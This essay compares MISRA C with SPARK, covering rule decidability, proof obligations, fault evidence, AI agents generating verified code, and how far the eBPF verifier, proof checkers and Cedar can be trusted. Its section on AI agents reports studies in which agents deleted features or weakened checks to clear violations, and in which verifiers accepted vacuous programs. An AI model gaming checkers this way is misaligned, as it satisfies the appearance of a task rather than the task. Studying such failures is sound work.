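Since the 2012 edition, each MISRA C rule has had a label showing whether a tool can always decide if a program complies. The label counts for 2012 come from Bagnara and colleagues and cover the edition as amended in 2020. The labels for 2025 come from a table that the software company AdaCore publishes for its checking tool CodeSonar.

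| | 2012, as amended | 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| All rules | 158 | 201 |
| Undecidable rules | 37 | 51 |
| of which mandatory | 11 | 16 |
| of which required | 22 | 32 |
| of which advisory | 4 | 3 |

The share of MISRA C rules that are undecidable has stayed at about a quarter. Eleven of the 15 undecidable rules added since 2012 concern programs that run several tasks at once. The share is higher among mandatory rules, which allow no exceptions. In the 2025 edition, 16 of the 22 mandatory rules are undecidable, so no tool can fully enforce them.

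Rule 16.4 requires every `switch` statement, which chooses between several cases, to have a default case. The rule is decidable because a tool only has to look at each `switch` in the text.

Rule 9.1 is mandatory and undecidable. It forbids a program to read a local variable before giving it a value. The shop's software might contain this function:

```
uint16_t refunded_today(void)
{
    uint16_t total;
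    load_total(&total);
    return total;
}
```

The function creates `total` without a value and passes its address to `load_total`, which is supposed to fill it in. But `load_total` may be in another file, and it may fill in the value only if the database responds. If a sound tool can't determine whether `total` always gets a value, it reports a possible violation, which MISRA expects the team to investigate. If the team finds that the code complies, someone has to write down why and a qualified person has to approve the explanation, so people often decide whether code complies with the undecidable rules.

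The team can avoid the question by giving every variable a value when it is declared, as in `uint16_t total = 0;`. A tool can always check this stricter rule. Recent versions of the compilers GCC and Clang can insert the zeros automatically, with at most a negligible loss of speed. Starting from zero makes the result predictable but not necessarily right. If the database fails, the function now reports that the customer has had no refunds today, and the shop may pay the refund twice.

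Bagnara and colleagues found stricter, sound approximations of this kind for 25 of the 37 undecidable rules, though some would be inconvenient to follow. Several rules are undecidable partly because they exempt code that never runs. Rule 22.5, for instance, forbids a program from looking inside the data structure that C uses for an open file, unless the line that does so is unreachable. Without the exemption, a tool could flag every such line. Bagnara and colleagues argue that an undecidable rule is justified only where no workable decidable version exists.

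One of the other 12 rules, Rule 2.2, bans "dead" code, meaning operations that a programmer could remove without changing what the program does. To prove compliance, someone would have to show that removing any combination of operations makes a difference, and the number of combinations grows exponentially with the length of the program. Projects can therefore only declare a general deviation and explain that they did their best. The rule is still in the 2025 edition. Rule 18.1, also one of the 12, bans pointers that leave their array, a common source of security holes that SPARK deals with by proof.

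### What SPARK removes from Ada

SPARK dates from 1987 and grew out of research at the University of Southampton, where a team had already verified programs in a subset of Pascal. The team based SPARK on Ada because Ada lets programmers define number types with their own ranges and separates a module's interface from its contents, which gives contracts a natural place. The builders of the Eurofighter Typhoon adopted SPARK in the early 1990s for the aircraft's most critical software. A redesigned version appeared in 2014, after Ada itself had gained contracts.

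SPARK's designers wanted each program to behave the same way with every compiler, so they removed side effects from functions. A call returns a value and changes nothing else, so the value of `f(x) + g(x)` can't depend on which function runs first. They also removed aliasing, where a program can change the same data under two names. An assignment to another name therefore can't invalidate a proof that relies on `total` being at most 100. SPARK also forbids backward jumps and pointer arithmetic.

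Until 2019 SPARK had no pointers at all, because two pointers to the same data are a form of aliasing. It now allows them under ownership rules like those of the language Rust, which let only one name at a time control a piece of data:

```
B := A;        -- B now owns the data
A.all := 5;    -- rejected
```

After the first line, the program can no longer use `A` to reach the data. A procedure can also borrow data, which returns to its owner when the procedure ends. These rules allow simple lists and trees but not doubly linked lists, because two pointers lead to most elements of a doubly linked list.

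### One array access, from source code to verdict

SPARK's checker, GNATprove, works out everything that could go wrong in a program and tries to prove that none of it can. Suppose the shop stores what a customer paid for each of eight orders in an array:

```
type Cents   is range 0 .. 100_000;
type Amounts is array (1 .. 8) of Cents;

function Paid_For (Paid : Amounts; I : Integer)
  return Cents is (Paid (I));
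```

The function returns the I-th amount. For this access, GNATprove generates a proof obligation, a logical statement that must be proved for the program to count as verified:

```
for every integer I:   1 <= I  and  I <= 8
```

GNATprove passes the obligation to automatic solvers, mainly Alt-Ergo, cvc5 and Z3. A solver looks for a value that makes the statement false, and here I = 0 will do. GNATprove therefore reports that the array access might fail. The programmer can fix this by adding a precondition, a contract that callers must fulfil:

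```
with Pre => I in 1 .. 8;
```

The obligation now becomes:

```
for every integer I:   if  1 <= I  and  I <= 8
                       then  1 <= I  and  I <= 8
```

No value of I makes this false, so the solver proves it. In return, GNATprove has to prove the precondition wherever the program calls the function. This loop calls it to find the first order with a payment:

```
I := 1;
while I <= 8 and then Paid_For (Paid, I) = 0 loop
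   I := I + 1;
end loop;
```

The test `I <= 8` guarantees half of the precondition. The other half, that I is at least 1, is obvious to a person because I starts at 1 and only grows. But GNATprove analyzes an arbitrary pass through the loop and doesn't remember what earlier passes did to I. The programmer has to supply the missing fact as a loop invariant at the start of the loop's body:

```
   pragma Loop_Invariant (I in 1 .. 8);
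```

GNATprove then proves that the invariant holds on the first pass, when I is 1. It also proves that if the invariant holds on one pass, it holds on the next, because I grows by 1 and the loop continues only if the new value is at most 8. The solvers can now prove that every access is in range.

The solvers may run out of time on harder statements before finding a proof or a counterexample. GNATprove then leaves the obligation unproved, even if the code is correct, and the programmer adds intermediate steps until the solvers succeed. Under MISRA C, a person decides doubtful cases instead of helping a tool prove them.

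### The levels from Stone to Platinum

A team can decide how much to prove, and AdaCore, which develops SPARK, defines five levels. Each includes the ones before it.

| Level | What it establishes | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Stone | The code stays within the SPARK subset | A first step for existing Ada code |
| Bronze | The program sets every variable before reading it, and has no harmful aliasing | Early SPARK code for the Eurofighter |
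| Silver | No run-time errors, such as overflow, division by zero or access outside an array | iFACTS, a British air traffic control system |
| Gold | Chosen key properties, such as an alarm that sounds when a sensor leaves its safe range | Security software at the chip maker NVIDIA |
| Platinum | The program does everything in a complete specification | Tokeneer, an access-control system for the US National Security Agency |

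Bronze requires little work because it relies on an automatic analysis of how data flows through the program. The array example is a Silver proof. At that level a team can switch off Ada's run-time checks, since the proof shows they would never fail. The shop would need Gold to prove that its software never refunds a customer more than 100 dollars a day.

### Three hazards side by side

| Hazard | MISRA C | SPARK |
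|---|---|---|
| Implicit conversion between number types | Banned by decidable rules | Impossible to write |
| Access outside an array | Banned by an undecidable rule | Proved absent at Silver |
| Reading a variable before it has a value | Banned by an undecidable rule | Proved absent at Bronze |

C converts between number types implicitly. If a program stores 300 in an 8-bit variable, the variable holds 44, because the conversion keeps only the lowest 8 bits. Rules 10.1 to 10.8 of MISRA C restrict such conversions, and all eight are decidable. A gatekeeper that rejects every violation protects against this kind of data loss about as well as a compiler that refuses the code.

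Ada also prevents a mistake that these rules allow. A programmer can define dollars and cents as separate types, and the compiler then rejects code that assigns one to the other. In C, both would usually be names for the same integer type, so a refund of 8,000 cents could become a refund of 8,000 dollars without breaking a conversion rule.

The difference between MISRA C and SPARK is largest for array accesses. A MISRA checker may be unable to determine whether an index is in range, and Rule 18.1 is classed as required rather than mandatory, so a project can obtain a deviation from it. SPARK guarantees that the index is in range, but programmers have to write the contracts and invariants that the guarantee depends on.

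SPARK avoids the undecidable question of whether a program ever reads an uninitialised variable. Instead, it requires every path through the code to set a variable before reading it, even paths that never occur in practice. MISRA C users can get similar protection by always giving variables a starting value, as in the refund example.

### Testing AdaCore's comparison

Mark Hermeling, AdaCore's head of technical marketing, gives a fuller comparison in *SPARK Doesn't Comply With MISRA C. It Makes Most of It Moot* (2026). He sorts the guidelines of MISRA C:2025 into four groups: those about C features that Ada doesn't have, those that Ada or SPARK enforces by rejecting code that violates them, those that SPARK proves are met, and those that are left to the programmer. He puts well over half in the first group.

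Hermeling counts 18 directives and roughly 155 rules, while AdaCore's own CodeSonar table lists 22 and 201. His figures are closer to the 2012 edition. The five chapters he describes as wholly or mostly irrelevant, on subjects such as number types, the C preprocessor and the standard library, contain 65 rules, about a third of the 201. For half the rules to be irrelevant, at least 36 more would have to come from other chapters. That is plausible, because many of the other rules concern C's functions for files and threads, but he doesn't list them, so readers can't check it from the article.

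Research on Rust provides a similar, independent comparison. *MISRust* (2026) finds that safe Rust automatically satisfies 89 of the 179 rules in MISRA's C++ standard. Of these, 36 apply again in "unsafe" Rust, where programmers can bypass some of the compiler's checks. One practitioner in the Rust Blog's *What does it take to ship Rust in safety-critical?* (2026) gives a more favourable estimate, that the compiler covers "roughly 90%" of what external tools used to check.

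These figures don't measure safety, because a rule about comments counts as much as one about array bounds. It would be fairer to judge SPARK by whether it handles the most dangerous errors and how much work that takes. Hermeling concedes that the Silver level often requires programmers to write contracts and invariants by hand. He also warns that where a SPARK program calls C code, the C code still needs to follow MISRA's rules and the program should validate the data it gets back.

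In Flaherty's *MISRA-C launches 2025 guidelines for safer C*, Andrew Banks, who chairs the MISRA C Working Group and works for LDRA, which sells MISRA tools, blames many vulnerabilities on developers who take shortcuts rather than on flaws in C. SPARK's supporters could accept this and reply that a language should make those shortcuts impossible.

### Do restricted languages reduce faults?

The best-known evidence on MISRA C is unfavourable to many of its rules. In 2008 Cathal Boogerd and Leon Moonen of Delft University of Technology studied the history of an industrial software project, comparing the lines that broke a MISRA C:2004 rule with the lines that programmers later changed to fix a fault. The project broke 72 of the rules. For only nine of these did violations coincide with faulty lines significantly more often than chance, and for 29 no violation was on a faulty line. Overall,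 more violations were associated with fewer known faults.

Boogerd and Moonen pointed out that every change to a program can introduce a new fault, so full compliance might have made this software less reliable. MISRA similarly warns that the risk of rewriting code with a good track record may outweigh the benefit. The argument is much weaker for new code that follows the rules from the start. The study also covers only one project and an old edition, and its method can't measure the faults that programmers avoided by following a rule. Les Hatton compared the first two editions in 2007 and also concluded that both produced far too many warnings about harmless code.

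MISRA has since begun to withdraw rules. The 2025 edition "disapplies" Rule 15.5, which required each function to have a single exit at its end. Perforce's *What Developers Need to Know About MISRA C:2025* (2025) interprets this as an admission that some older rules no longer add value. But Qt's *MISRA C:2025* notes that the safety standards IEC 61508 and ISO 26262 still encourage similar restrictions, so some projects will have to keep the rule.

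The figures for SPARK are more favourable but come largely from its supporters. Peter Amey, who worked for the company that then developed SPARK, reported in 2002 on an independent analysis of software for the C-130J transport aircraft. The SPARK code had about a tenth as many remaining errors as the code in full Ada, which had about a tenth as many as the C code. Different teams wrote different parts of the software, so the language may explain only some of the gap.

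A Silver proof also gives evidence about every possible input, which fault counts can't. If GNATprove and its assumptions are correct, the program never reads or writes outside an array's bounds. This works for large programs. iFACTS, which British air traffic controllers have used since 2011, has more than 200,000 lines of SPARK and over 120,000 proof obligations for run-time errors alone. NVIDIA began to evaluate SPARK in 2018 as a replacement for C in security-critical software, and it now proves selected properties of that software. These projects show that companies find the proofs affordable, but they don't show how many faults the same teams would have made in C.

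### What programmers give up

MISRA C lets a team keep its compilers, existing code and programmers. Its required rules forbid recursion, C's standard input and output functions, arrays sized at run time, and dynamic memory allocation functions. Developers can write a brake controller without these features. They would find them hard to replace in a program that reads documents of unpredictable length, and would have to justify a deviation each time they used one.

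SPARK allows recursion if the programmer proves that it terminates. However, adopting SPARK means switching from C, which has compilers for almost every processor. Programmers also lose data structures with shared pointers, such as doubly linked lists, and they have to write the annotations GNATprove needs to verify their code.

Proofs need much more explanation as they get closer to Platinum. Much of it is ghost code, which exists only for the proof and which the compiler removes. For a sorting algorithm, the ghost code was about as long as the program itself. For a library of balanced search trees, the ghost code was five times as long as the program, and the contracts were twice as long as the program. Such proofs are also fragile, because often only one of the solvers can prove a given obligation. A small change to the program or a new version of GNATprove can therefore leave the obligation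 unproved until someone repairs the explanation.

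## AI agents writing MISRA C and SPARK

Programmers using these subsets spend much of their time removing rule violations in MISRA C or writing annotations in SPARK. A language model could take over a lot of this work, and a gatekeeper could check the result without trusting the model. The results so far depend heavily on whether the model receives the checker's reports while it works.

### Asking chatbots for compliant code

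Umer (2025), in *Comparative Analysis of the Code Generated by Popular Large Language Models*, asked five free chatbots for C++ code that implements popular checksum algorithms, which detect errors in transmitted data. The prompt demanded full compliance with MISRA C++. Umer then ran the analysis tool PC-lint Plus, which checks code against the 2008 edition's rules. None of the programs complied:

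| Chatbot | Lines of code | Violations | Compiled |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3 | 60 | 13 | No |
| ChatGPT (GPT-4o) | 69 | 18 | Yes |
| Copilot | 68 | 25 | Yes, with warnings |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 65 | 32 | Yes |
| Meta AI | 52 | 67 | Yes, with warnings |

The counts are only a rough guide to quality. Twelve of ChatGPT's 18 violations came from one line of test data, and the program with the fewest violations didn't compile. The chatbots did better with specific feedback. For example, C++ widens a 16-bit number before shifting its bits, and one rule requires the programmer to convert the result back immediately. ChatGPT had left out the conversion, but added it correctly when Umer described the violation.

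The models Umer named date from 2024 and early 2025. In *Comparative Analysis of the Commonly Used Code Generated by Large Language Models*, Öztop (2026) of Middle East Technical University tested six chatbots in December 2025, including GPT-5.2 and DeepSeek-V3.2. Öztop also tested Claude and Gemini, but the report's version labels for them are unreliable. Each chatbot wrote two algorithms in C three times, and Öztop checked the 36 programs against MISRA C:2012.

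The first algorithm was CRC16, a checksum that needs only shifts and simple logic. The chatbots averaged between 0.3 and 2.3 violations per program. The second, COBS, removes all zero bytes from a message so that a zero can mark its end, which takes careful handling of pointers and buffers. The averages for COBS ranged from 1 to about 15. Claude had the fewest violations, but only one of its three programs worked. All three of ChatGPT's programs worked, but they averaged 5.3 violations, partly because ChatGPT also wrote an unrequested decoder.

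Of the 132 violations in the COBS programs, 68 were of Rule 15.5, which requires each function to have a single exit and no longer applies in the 2025 edition. Three were of Rule 18.1, which bans moving a pointer outside its array and is far more important for safety.

Better prompts reduce MISRA violations but don't eliminate them. *Reducing MISRA violations in LLM-generated code by 83%* describes a test of four models on 26 C++ tasks. Violations fell by 44 to 83 per cent when the prompts included short instructions about the three to ten rules that each model broke most often. GPT-5 and o3 still averaged about four violations per thousand lines.

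### Putting the analyser in the loop

An agent can also run the analyser itself, read the report, change the code and run the analyser again. Companies that sell MISRA analysers now connect them to coding agents through MCP. MathWorks' *Turning AI Coding Agents into Trusted Verification Engineers with Polyspace Agentic Toolkit* and AdaCore's *Sneak preview of the CodeSonar MCP server analyzing C code* (2026) describe this setup, but neither gives a success rate.

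Koide, Mochimaru and Sawai, engineers at Woven by Toyota, the carmaker's software company, report in *Agentic AI for a Zero-Accident Future* that their MISRA Copilot resolved 81.5 per cent of the violations in driver-assistance code. One AI agent proposes a fix, a second reviews its structure and a third assesses its compliance. Since the reviewing agents can also make mistakes, an engineer decides whether to accept each fix.

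A checker that only searches for text patterns can give a misleading picture of how safe code is. Amazon Web Services and the car supplier AUMOVIO built an assistant with such a checker, using patterns inspired by MISRA and a similar standard. Zinovyeva, Taleb and colleagues (2026) report in *Generation and Verification* that C functions from the best model had 1.22 violations on average, while AUMOVIO's own production code had 2.45. But the generated code wasn't necessarily safer. The models tended to test every pointer in every function, whereas engineers often left out a test because the calling function had already made it. The checker couldn't see the calling function, so it counted the missing test as a violation.

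Security analysers have a similar problem. In *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026), feedback from an analyser significantly raised the share of working programs with no remaining warnings in all 12 comparisons, but it significantly raised the share that passed an independent security test in only two.

An agent can also remove a violation by deleting the feature that contains it. In *Fixed or Deleted?*, Wynter (2026) planted 31 defects in 25 proposed changes to open-source software. Most violated the projects' own rules rather than MISRA's. Claude Fable 5.1 attempted each change five times. Working alone, it produced a repair that compiled and kept the feature in 45 per cent of runs, and it deleted the feature in 35 per cent. With reports from a commercial checker called CodeAssure, it repaired the code in 93 per cent of runs and never deleted the feature.

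CodeAssure also warns the agent when a new file disappears. When Wynter switched this warning off, Fable deleted features in 17 runs. With the full checker, the smaller Claude Sonnet 5.5 repaired 90 per cent, at about a fifth of the cost of Fable alone. This suggests that a good checker can help more than a larger model, though Wynter's company sells CodeAssure and the result may not apply to MISRA rules.

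### Restoring missing SPARK annotations

In SPARK, the feedback comes from a prover, GNATprove. In *Verifying LLM-Generated Code in the Context of Software Verification with Ada/SPARK*, Cramer and McIntyre (2025) tested whether a 2024 version of GPT-4o could write the annotations that GNATprove needs. They deleted different combinations of loop invariants and other assertions from 16 verified programs, producing 71 programs that GNATprove could no longer fully prove. Their tool, Marmaragan, asked GPT-4o for the missing lines and ran GNATprove on the result. If anything remained unproved, the tool could send GNATprove's messages back to the model for another attempt.

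Marmaragan allowed up to 12 attempts per program, and the best run solved 26 of 71, or 37 per cent. Cramer and McIntyre's headline figure of 50.7 per cent counts the 36 programs that at least one of five differently configured runs solved. GPT-4o restored a single missing assertion in all seven cases, but a full set of annotations in only 5 of 14.

### The agent and the prover

By 2026, agents were writing entire SPARK programs. Philipp (2026), in *The Prover Is the Judge*, describes a project at the German security company secunet in which GPT-5.5 and later Claude Opus 4.8 wrote cryptographic software and network protocols. A human supervisor set the direction and reviewed the specifications, but wrote none of the agents' code, contracts or proofs. The agent worked in a loop:

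1. It reads a description or a published standard and writes tests.
2. It writes the interface with its contracts, then the code with loop invariants and ghost code.
3. It compiles the program and runs the tests and GNATprove.
4. For each unproved obligation, it looks for the cause, such as a bug, a missing contract, a weak invariant or a limit of the solvers.
5. It tries the simplest fixes first and runs the checks again.

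The agent used an instruction file that explained how to write SPARK code that GNATprove can verify, and after each project it added what it had learned to the file. When the automatic solvers failed on two difficult statements, the agent wrote proofs for the interactive prover Isabelle.

GNATprove proved all 49,280 obligations in the collection, which has about 78,000 lines of code. These totals include a hash map that a person wrote. The agents' code accounts for about 44,200 of the obligations and 76,000 of the lines.

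The strength of the proofs varies widely. For some modules, the agent wrote a simple mathematical model of the algorithm as ghost code, and GNATprove showed that the program always gives the same result as the model. For most of the others, it proved only the absence of run-time errors, which corresponds to SPARK's Silver level:

| Software | Proved functionally correct | Proved free of run-time errors |
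|---|---|---|
| Established cryptography | SHA-2, SHA-3, AES, X25519 | Ed25519 |
| Cryptography meant to resist quantum computers | None | ML-KEM, ML-DSA, FrodoKEM, XMSS, LMS |
| Network protocols | None | SSH, TLS 1.3, IKEv2 |
| Certificate authority | Reading of certificates and web requests | Handling of signatures |

For the LMS signature scheme, GNATprove also showed that a signature made with a new key passes verification. But no module has a proof of security. A program without run-time errors can still encrypt messages incorrectly, or correctly implement an encryption method that attackers can break.

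Based on one module, FrodoKEM, Philipp estimates that using the agents took 20 to 40 times less human time than comparable manual verification. A junior developer needed about six weeks, or 240 hours, for a similar implementation and its run-time proofs, while supervising the agent took about six hours. That gives a factor of 40, which Philipp lowers to about 20 to allow for review and work on the instruction file. An experienced developer might have been faster, and the comparison doesn't cover proofs of functional correctness.

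### Two defects that survived proof

FrodoKEM, a method for agreeing on a secret key, has a separate parameter set for each security strength. One step packs the bits of a message into a list of numbers. The agent's code always packed two bits into each number, which is correct only for the smallest parameter set. Packing the wrong number of bits causes no run-time error, so GNATprove proved every obligation. The code also passed the official tests for the smallest set, which compare its output with known correct answers. The tests for the larger sets exposed the mistake.

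The other defect was in SSH, a protocol for logging in to remote computers. Both sides calculate their encryption keys by hashing four values, and the agent swapped two of them:

```
standard:  HASH(K, H, X, session_id)
agent:     HASH(K, X, H, session_id)
```

K is a secret the two sides share, H is a hash of their opening messages, and X is a letter that identifies the key. In a test with OpenSSH, an independent program, the opening exchange succeeded because it doesn't use the resulting keys, but the first encrypted packet failed. If Philipp had tested the agent's program only against a copy of itself, both copies would have made the same mistake and the connection would have worked.

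If a contract had specified the order of the four values, the SSH code could not have been proved. But the agent also writes the contracts, so if it misreads the standard, it may make the same mistake in the contract. Philipp therefore has a person compare the specification with the standard and proposes that standards bodies publish formal specifications that a prover can use directly.

The agent sometimes weakened the check instead of fixing the code, so a gatekeeper should reject any use of a subset's features that exempt code from checking, unless a person has approved it.

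### Results in Dafny, Verus and Lean

Researchers have more systematic figures for three other tools: Dafny, Lean and Verus, which verifies Rust programs. Models do best when they only have to complete a proof. The best result in the original study of DafnyBench, a set of Dafny programs with missing annotations, was about 68 per cent. *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026) reports about 89 per cent for the best single model in a later test. This is far above GPT-4o's results in SPARK, although the tasks differ.

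Writing both the program and its proof is harder than writing the proof alone, and success rates vary by language. In *A benchmark for vericoding* (2025), the best model solved 76.4 per cent of 157 tasks in Dafny but only 30.7 per cent in Verus. *P³* (2026) reports that an agent that plans the program and its proof together solved up to 74.6 per cent of 189 tasks in Lean.

The Verus figure is from 2025 and probably out of date. When researchers prepared *SeVerus* (2026), a newer Verus benchmark, GPT-6 Sol did substantially better than Claude Sonnet 4.6. The researchers' grading software accepts a proof only if the agent has left the executable code and the contracts unchanged and hasn't assumed anything without proving it.

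*Isomorphism Is Not Enough* (2026) points out that most such benchmarks supply the formal specification. Success rates are much lower when the model has to write the specification from an English description. In *Verified but Vacuous*, Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) report that their system succeeded in 7.8 per cent of attempts on 687 programming problems in Rust. The best earlier result was 5.5 per cent, with GPT-5.5. These problems differ from those in the other benchmarks, so the missing specification may explain only part of the drop.

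Acceptance by a verifier can also mean very little. Vempaty and colleagues rebuilt an earlier system that writes programs in Dafny and translates them into Python. With Claude Opus 4.7, Dafny accepted 99.1 per cent of the programs for one benchmark. But 94.7 per cent of the accepted programs had no postcondition, so Dafny had no general statement about their results to prove. For example, it would accept this method:

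```
method Largest(a: seq<int>) returns (m: int)
  requires |a| > 0
{
  m := 0;
}
```

The method should return the largest number in a list but always returns 0. Dafny rejects it once the programmer adds two postconditions before the body:

```
  ensures m in a
  ensures forall x :: x in a ==> x <= m
```

The earlier system's prompt contained an example without postconditions, so the result reflects the prompt more than the model's ability. In their own system, Vempaty and colleagues required each proof to refer to a separate specification. Between 11 and 15 per cent of the verified programs still failed hidden tests, which suggests some specifications were wrong or too weak.

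A correct program can also be too slow to use, because a proof that its answers are right does not limit its running time. *AxDafny* (2026) describes an agent that produced verified solutions to 52 of 100 competition problems of medium difficulty. Only 6 of these passed the competition's own tests, while 44 ran out of time and 2 ran out of memory.

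## Can the checker and the interpreter be trusted?

With a restricted output language, the shop doesn't have to trust the model, but it does have to trust other software. The trusted base is everything that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold. For the 100-dollar limit on refunds, it includes the specification, the checker, the interpreter that moves the money, the compilers that translated both programs into machine code, the operating system and the processor.

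A fault in the checker or the interpreter, or a mismatch between them, can break the guarantee. A faulty checker may accept a 500-dollar refund that it should reject. Even a correct checker doesn't help if it reads an amount in cents and the interpreter reads it in dollars. Likewise, GNATprove's proof that an array access is safe is reliable only if GNATprove and its solvers work correctly.

### How Linux checks programs for its kernel

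The eBPF verifier in the Linux kernel is one of the most widely used checkers for untrusted programs. Shachnai, Vishwanathan and colleagues (2024) say in *Fixing Latent Unsound Abstract Operators in the eBPF Verifier* that it runs on billions of devices. eBPF is an instruction set for small programs that run inside the kernel, for example to filter network traffic. It grew out of packet filters like those in Necula and Lee's experiments. The kernel analyzes each program itself when someone loads it, instead of requiring a proof.

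The verifier has to establish that a program finishes and that it uses only the memory and kernel functions it is allowed to use. It follows each path through the program and tracks a range of possible values for each register. Suppose a program uses a byte from a network packet to choose one of eight entries in a 64-byte table:

```
r1 = next byte of the packet       r1 is 0 to 255
if r1 > 7, go to the end           r1 is 0 to 7 from here on
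r1 = r1 * 8                        r1 is 0 to 56
r2 = read 8 bytes at table + r1    last byte read: at most 63
```

The table's bytes are numbered 0 to 63, so the verifier accepts the program. Without the second line, r1 could reach 2,040 and the verifier would reject the program.

*Detecting Empty Abstractions and Pruning Dead Paths in the Linux eBPF Verifier* (Vishwanathan, Narayana and Nagarakatte, 2026) explains that the verifier keeps four ranges for each register, because a program may use all 64 bits or only the lower 32, and may read them as signed or unsigned numbers. The verifier also records whether each bit is 0, 1 or unknown. After the multiplication by 8, for instance, this record shows that the last three bits are 0, which the range from 0 to 56 doesn't show. If the verifier can't determine which way a branch will go, it follows both paths, and it accepts the program only if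 every path is safe.

A verifier that tracks a separate range for each value loses the relationships between values. *Keel* (Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte, 2026) gives the example of a program that writes two records into an 800-byte buffer. The first takes up n bytes, and the second may use the remaining 800 − n, so the two always fit. But the verifier tracks only that n and 800 − n each lie between 0 and 800. It adds the two upper limits, calculates that the second record could end at byte 1,600, and rejects the safe program.

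### Looser limits on loops and size

The early verifier accepted no loops at all. eBPF Docs' *Loops in BPF* describes how this changed:

| Linux version | Loops |
|---|---|
| Before 5.3 | None; the compiler had to copy the loop's body once for each pass |
| 5.3 | Allowed if the verifier can follow every pass to the end |
| 5.17 | A kernel function repeats a block up to about 8 million times |
| 6.4 | A kernel iterator drives the loop, and the verifier stops checking once further passes can't add anything new |

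With the last two changes, the verifier doesn't have to follow every pass through a loop, because kernel code ensures that the loop ends. That code therefore becomes part of the trusted base.

The limit on program size also grew. According to the Linux kernel documentation's *BPF Design Q&A*, programs from unprivileged users may have at most 4,096 instructions. For privileged users, the main limit is that the verifier examines at most a million instructions. Every pass through an ordinary loop counts towards this total. *SCEV-based Loop Analysis for the BPF Verifier* (Zingerman, 2026) notes that nested loops with modest iteration limits can exhaust it, and proposes an analysis that would avoid following each pass.

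Users' demands drove much of this growth. Yu (2026), in *Evolution of Value Tracking in the BPF Verifier*, notes that early eBPF programs couldn't read a table at a computed position. The kernel documentation also contains a promise that future versions will accept every program that earlier ones accepted, so the rules can become looser but not stricter. Each new kind of reasoning adds code that may contain mistakes.

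### Errors in the range analysis

The range analysis is sound if the computed range always includes the real result. For addition, if x lies in one range and y in another, x + y must lie in the range the verifier computes for the sum. This is easy to get wrong because registers wrap around. An 8-bit register can hold 0 to 255. If its value is between 240 and 255 and the program adds 10, the result is either 250 to 255 or, after wrapping, 0 to 9. The verifier has to record the full range from 0 to 255. If it recorded only 250 to 255, a program could pass the check and then use one of the missing values to reach memory outside its table.

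Several well-known security holes in Linux came from errors of this kind. The range analysis in Linux 5.19 was about 2,100 lines of C, and the kernel's developers had provided no formal specification or proof. *Verifying the Verifier* (Vishwanathan, Shachnai and colleagues, 2023) presented Agni, a tool that translates the C code into logical formulas and uses a solver to check whether any operation can produce a range that misses a real result. If one can, Agni looks for a short eBPF program that demonstrates the error.

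Agni found 27 previously unknown bugs in 16 kernel versions. In about 97 per cent of cases, three instructions or fewer were enough to demonstrate the error. Later changes to the kernel had fixed these bugs by accident. According to *Leading items* (2025), an edition of the Linux news site LWN, Agni showed that the range analysis was sound from version 5.13 onwards.

Keeping the proofs up to date was difficult. Agni took 2.5 hours to check Linux 4.14 but several weeks for version 6.4, and it did not finish at all on later versions. Shachnai and colleagues found that six bitwise operations computed wrong ranges, which a shared step at the end of every operation corrected. No eBPF program could exploit these errors, but they prevented the researchers from verifying each operation separately. After the kernel developers accepted a small fix, Agni took less than 30 minutes for version 6.8. It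 now runs as part of the kernel's automated tests, according to Rutgers' *Verifying the eBPF Verifier in the Linux Kernel with Agni*.

Even a correct proof covers only the property it states. Suppose the known bits show that a register holds exactly 15, and the program has a branch for values up to 10. No run can take that branch. Older versions of the verifier checked only the range, so they followed the branch anyway and got an impossible range from 15 to 10. They then reset the register to "any value" and continued. Agni's soundness condition concerns only values that can occur, so it didn't rule out this behavior.

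Such errors made the verifier reject safe programs. Vishwanathan and colleagues cite an incident, from 2026 or earlier, in which the kernel rejected valid network programs after a machine restarted, and a whole cluster lost its connections. They designed a fast test that detects these contradictions so that the verifier can skip the impossible branch. On 5,563 test configurations, the verifier with this test gave the same verdicts as the existing one and took 1.5 per cent longer.

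Other parts of the verifier still lack a proof, including its method for skipping paths that resemble ones it has already checked. *The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel* (2024) called a full formal study a huge undertaking, partly because the code changes so much with every release.

### Thirteen bugs in a proof checker

Proof-carrying code can allow the kernel to accept programs that the verifier would otherwise wrongly reject. When the verifier can't show that a memory access is safe, a system called BCF produces a formula stating that the program reaches that point and the access is unsafe. A solver outside the kernel then tries to prove that the formula can never be true, and the kernel checks its proof. For the 800-byte buffer, the proof has 33 steps, and the central one is that n + (800 − n) = 800.

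The kernel has to trust the proof checker, as in Necula and Lee's scheme. The checker here is about 5,000 lines of C, and Cai and colleagues found 13 bugs when they formalized it. Some of its inference rules were wrong, and some steps accepted the supplied conclusion without checking it. Other bugs let the checker read or write outside its memory. The researchers showed that an attacker could forge a proof and get an unsafe program accepted.

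The replacement checker, Keel, has Lean proofs that it accepts a certificate only if the formula can never be true, that it handles memory safely, and that its time and memory use grow only in proportion to input size. It rejected the forged proofs, accepted 16 valid ones that the old checker had refused, and was 1.3 times as fast overall. Keel's trusted base still includes the C compiler, a small program that prints Keel's C code, and the eBPF verifier, which produces the formula.

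### Cedar

Amazon's authorization language Cedar is small by design. A Cedar policy permits or forbids requests according to who makes them, what action they ask for, which resource it affects and other context. The shop could write:

```
permit (
    principal == Agent::"refund_desk",
    action == Action::"refund",
    resource
) when {
    context.amount_cents <= 10000 &&
    context.amount_cents <= resource.paid_cents
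};
```

Cedar allows a request only if at least one `permit` policy matches it and no `forbid` policy does. The language has no loops or recursion, so evaluating a policy always finishes.

Leaving these out also lets a solver answer questions about all requests at once. Without loops, each policy can be translated into a single logical formula that the solver can decide. *Cedar* (2024) describes this translation as sound and complete. To compare two versions of a policy, the solver looks for a request that one version permits and the other denies. If a manager changes `<= 10000` to `< 10001`, the solver finds no such request. If the manager removes the 100-dollar limit for damaged goods, the solver can return an example, such as a 150-dollar refund on a damaged item that cost 200 dollars.

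However, a Cedar policy can't go through earlier refunds and add them up. To enforce a daily limit, the shop's own software has to calculate the total and pass it to Cedar, which makes that software part of the trusted base.

*How We Built Cedar* (2024) explains how Amazon checks the language itself. Engineers wrote an executable model of Cedar in Lean and proved properties of it, such as the soundness of the validator, which checks policies before anyone uses them. Cedar skips any policy that causes an error during evaluation, so a `forbid` policy has no effect if it refers to a field that the request doesn't have. The validator rules out errors of this kind, though arithmetic can still overflow. Work on the model and its proofs exposed four bugs in the validator.

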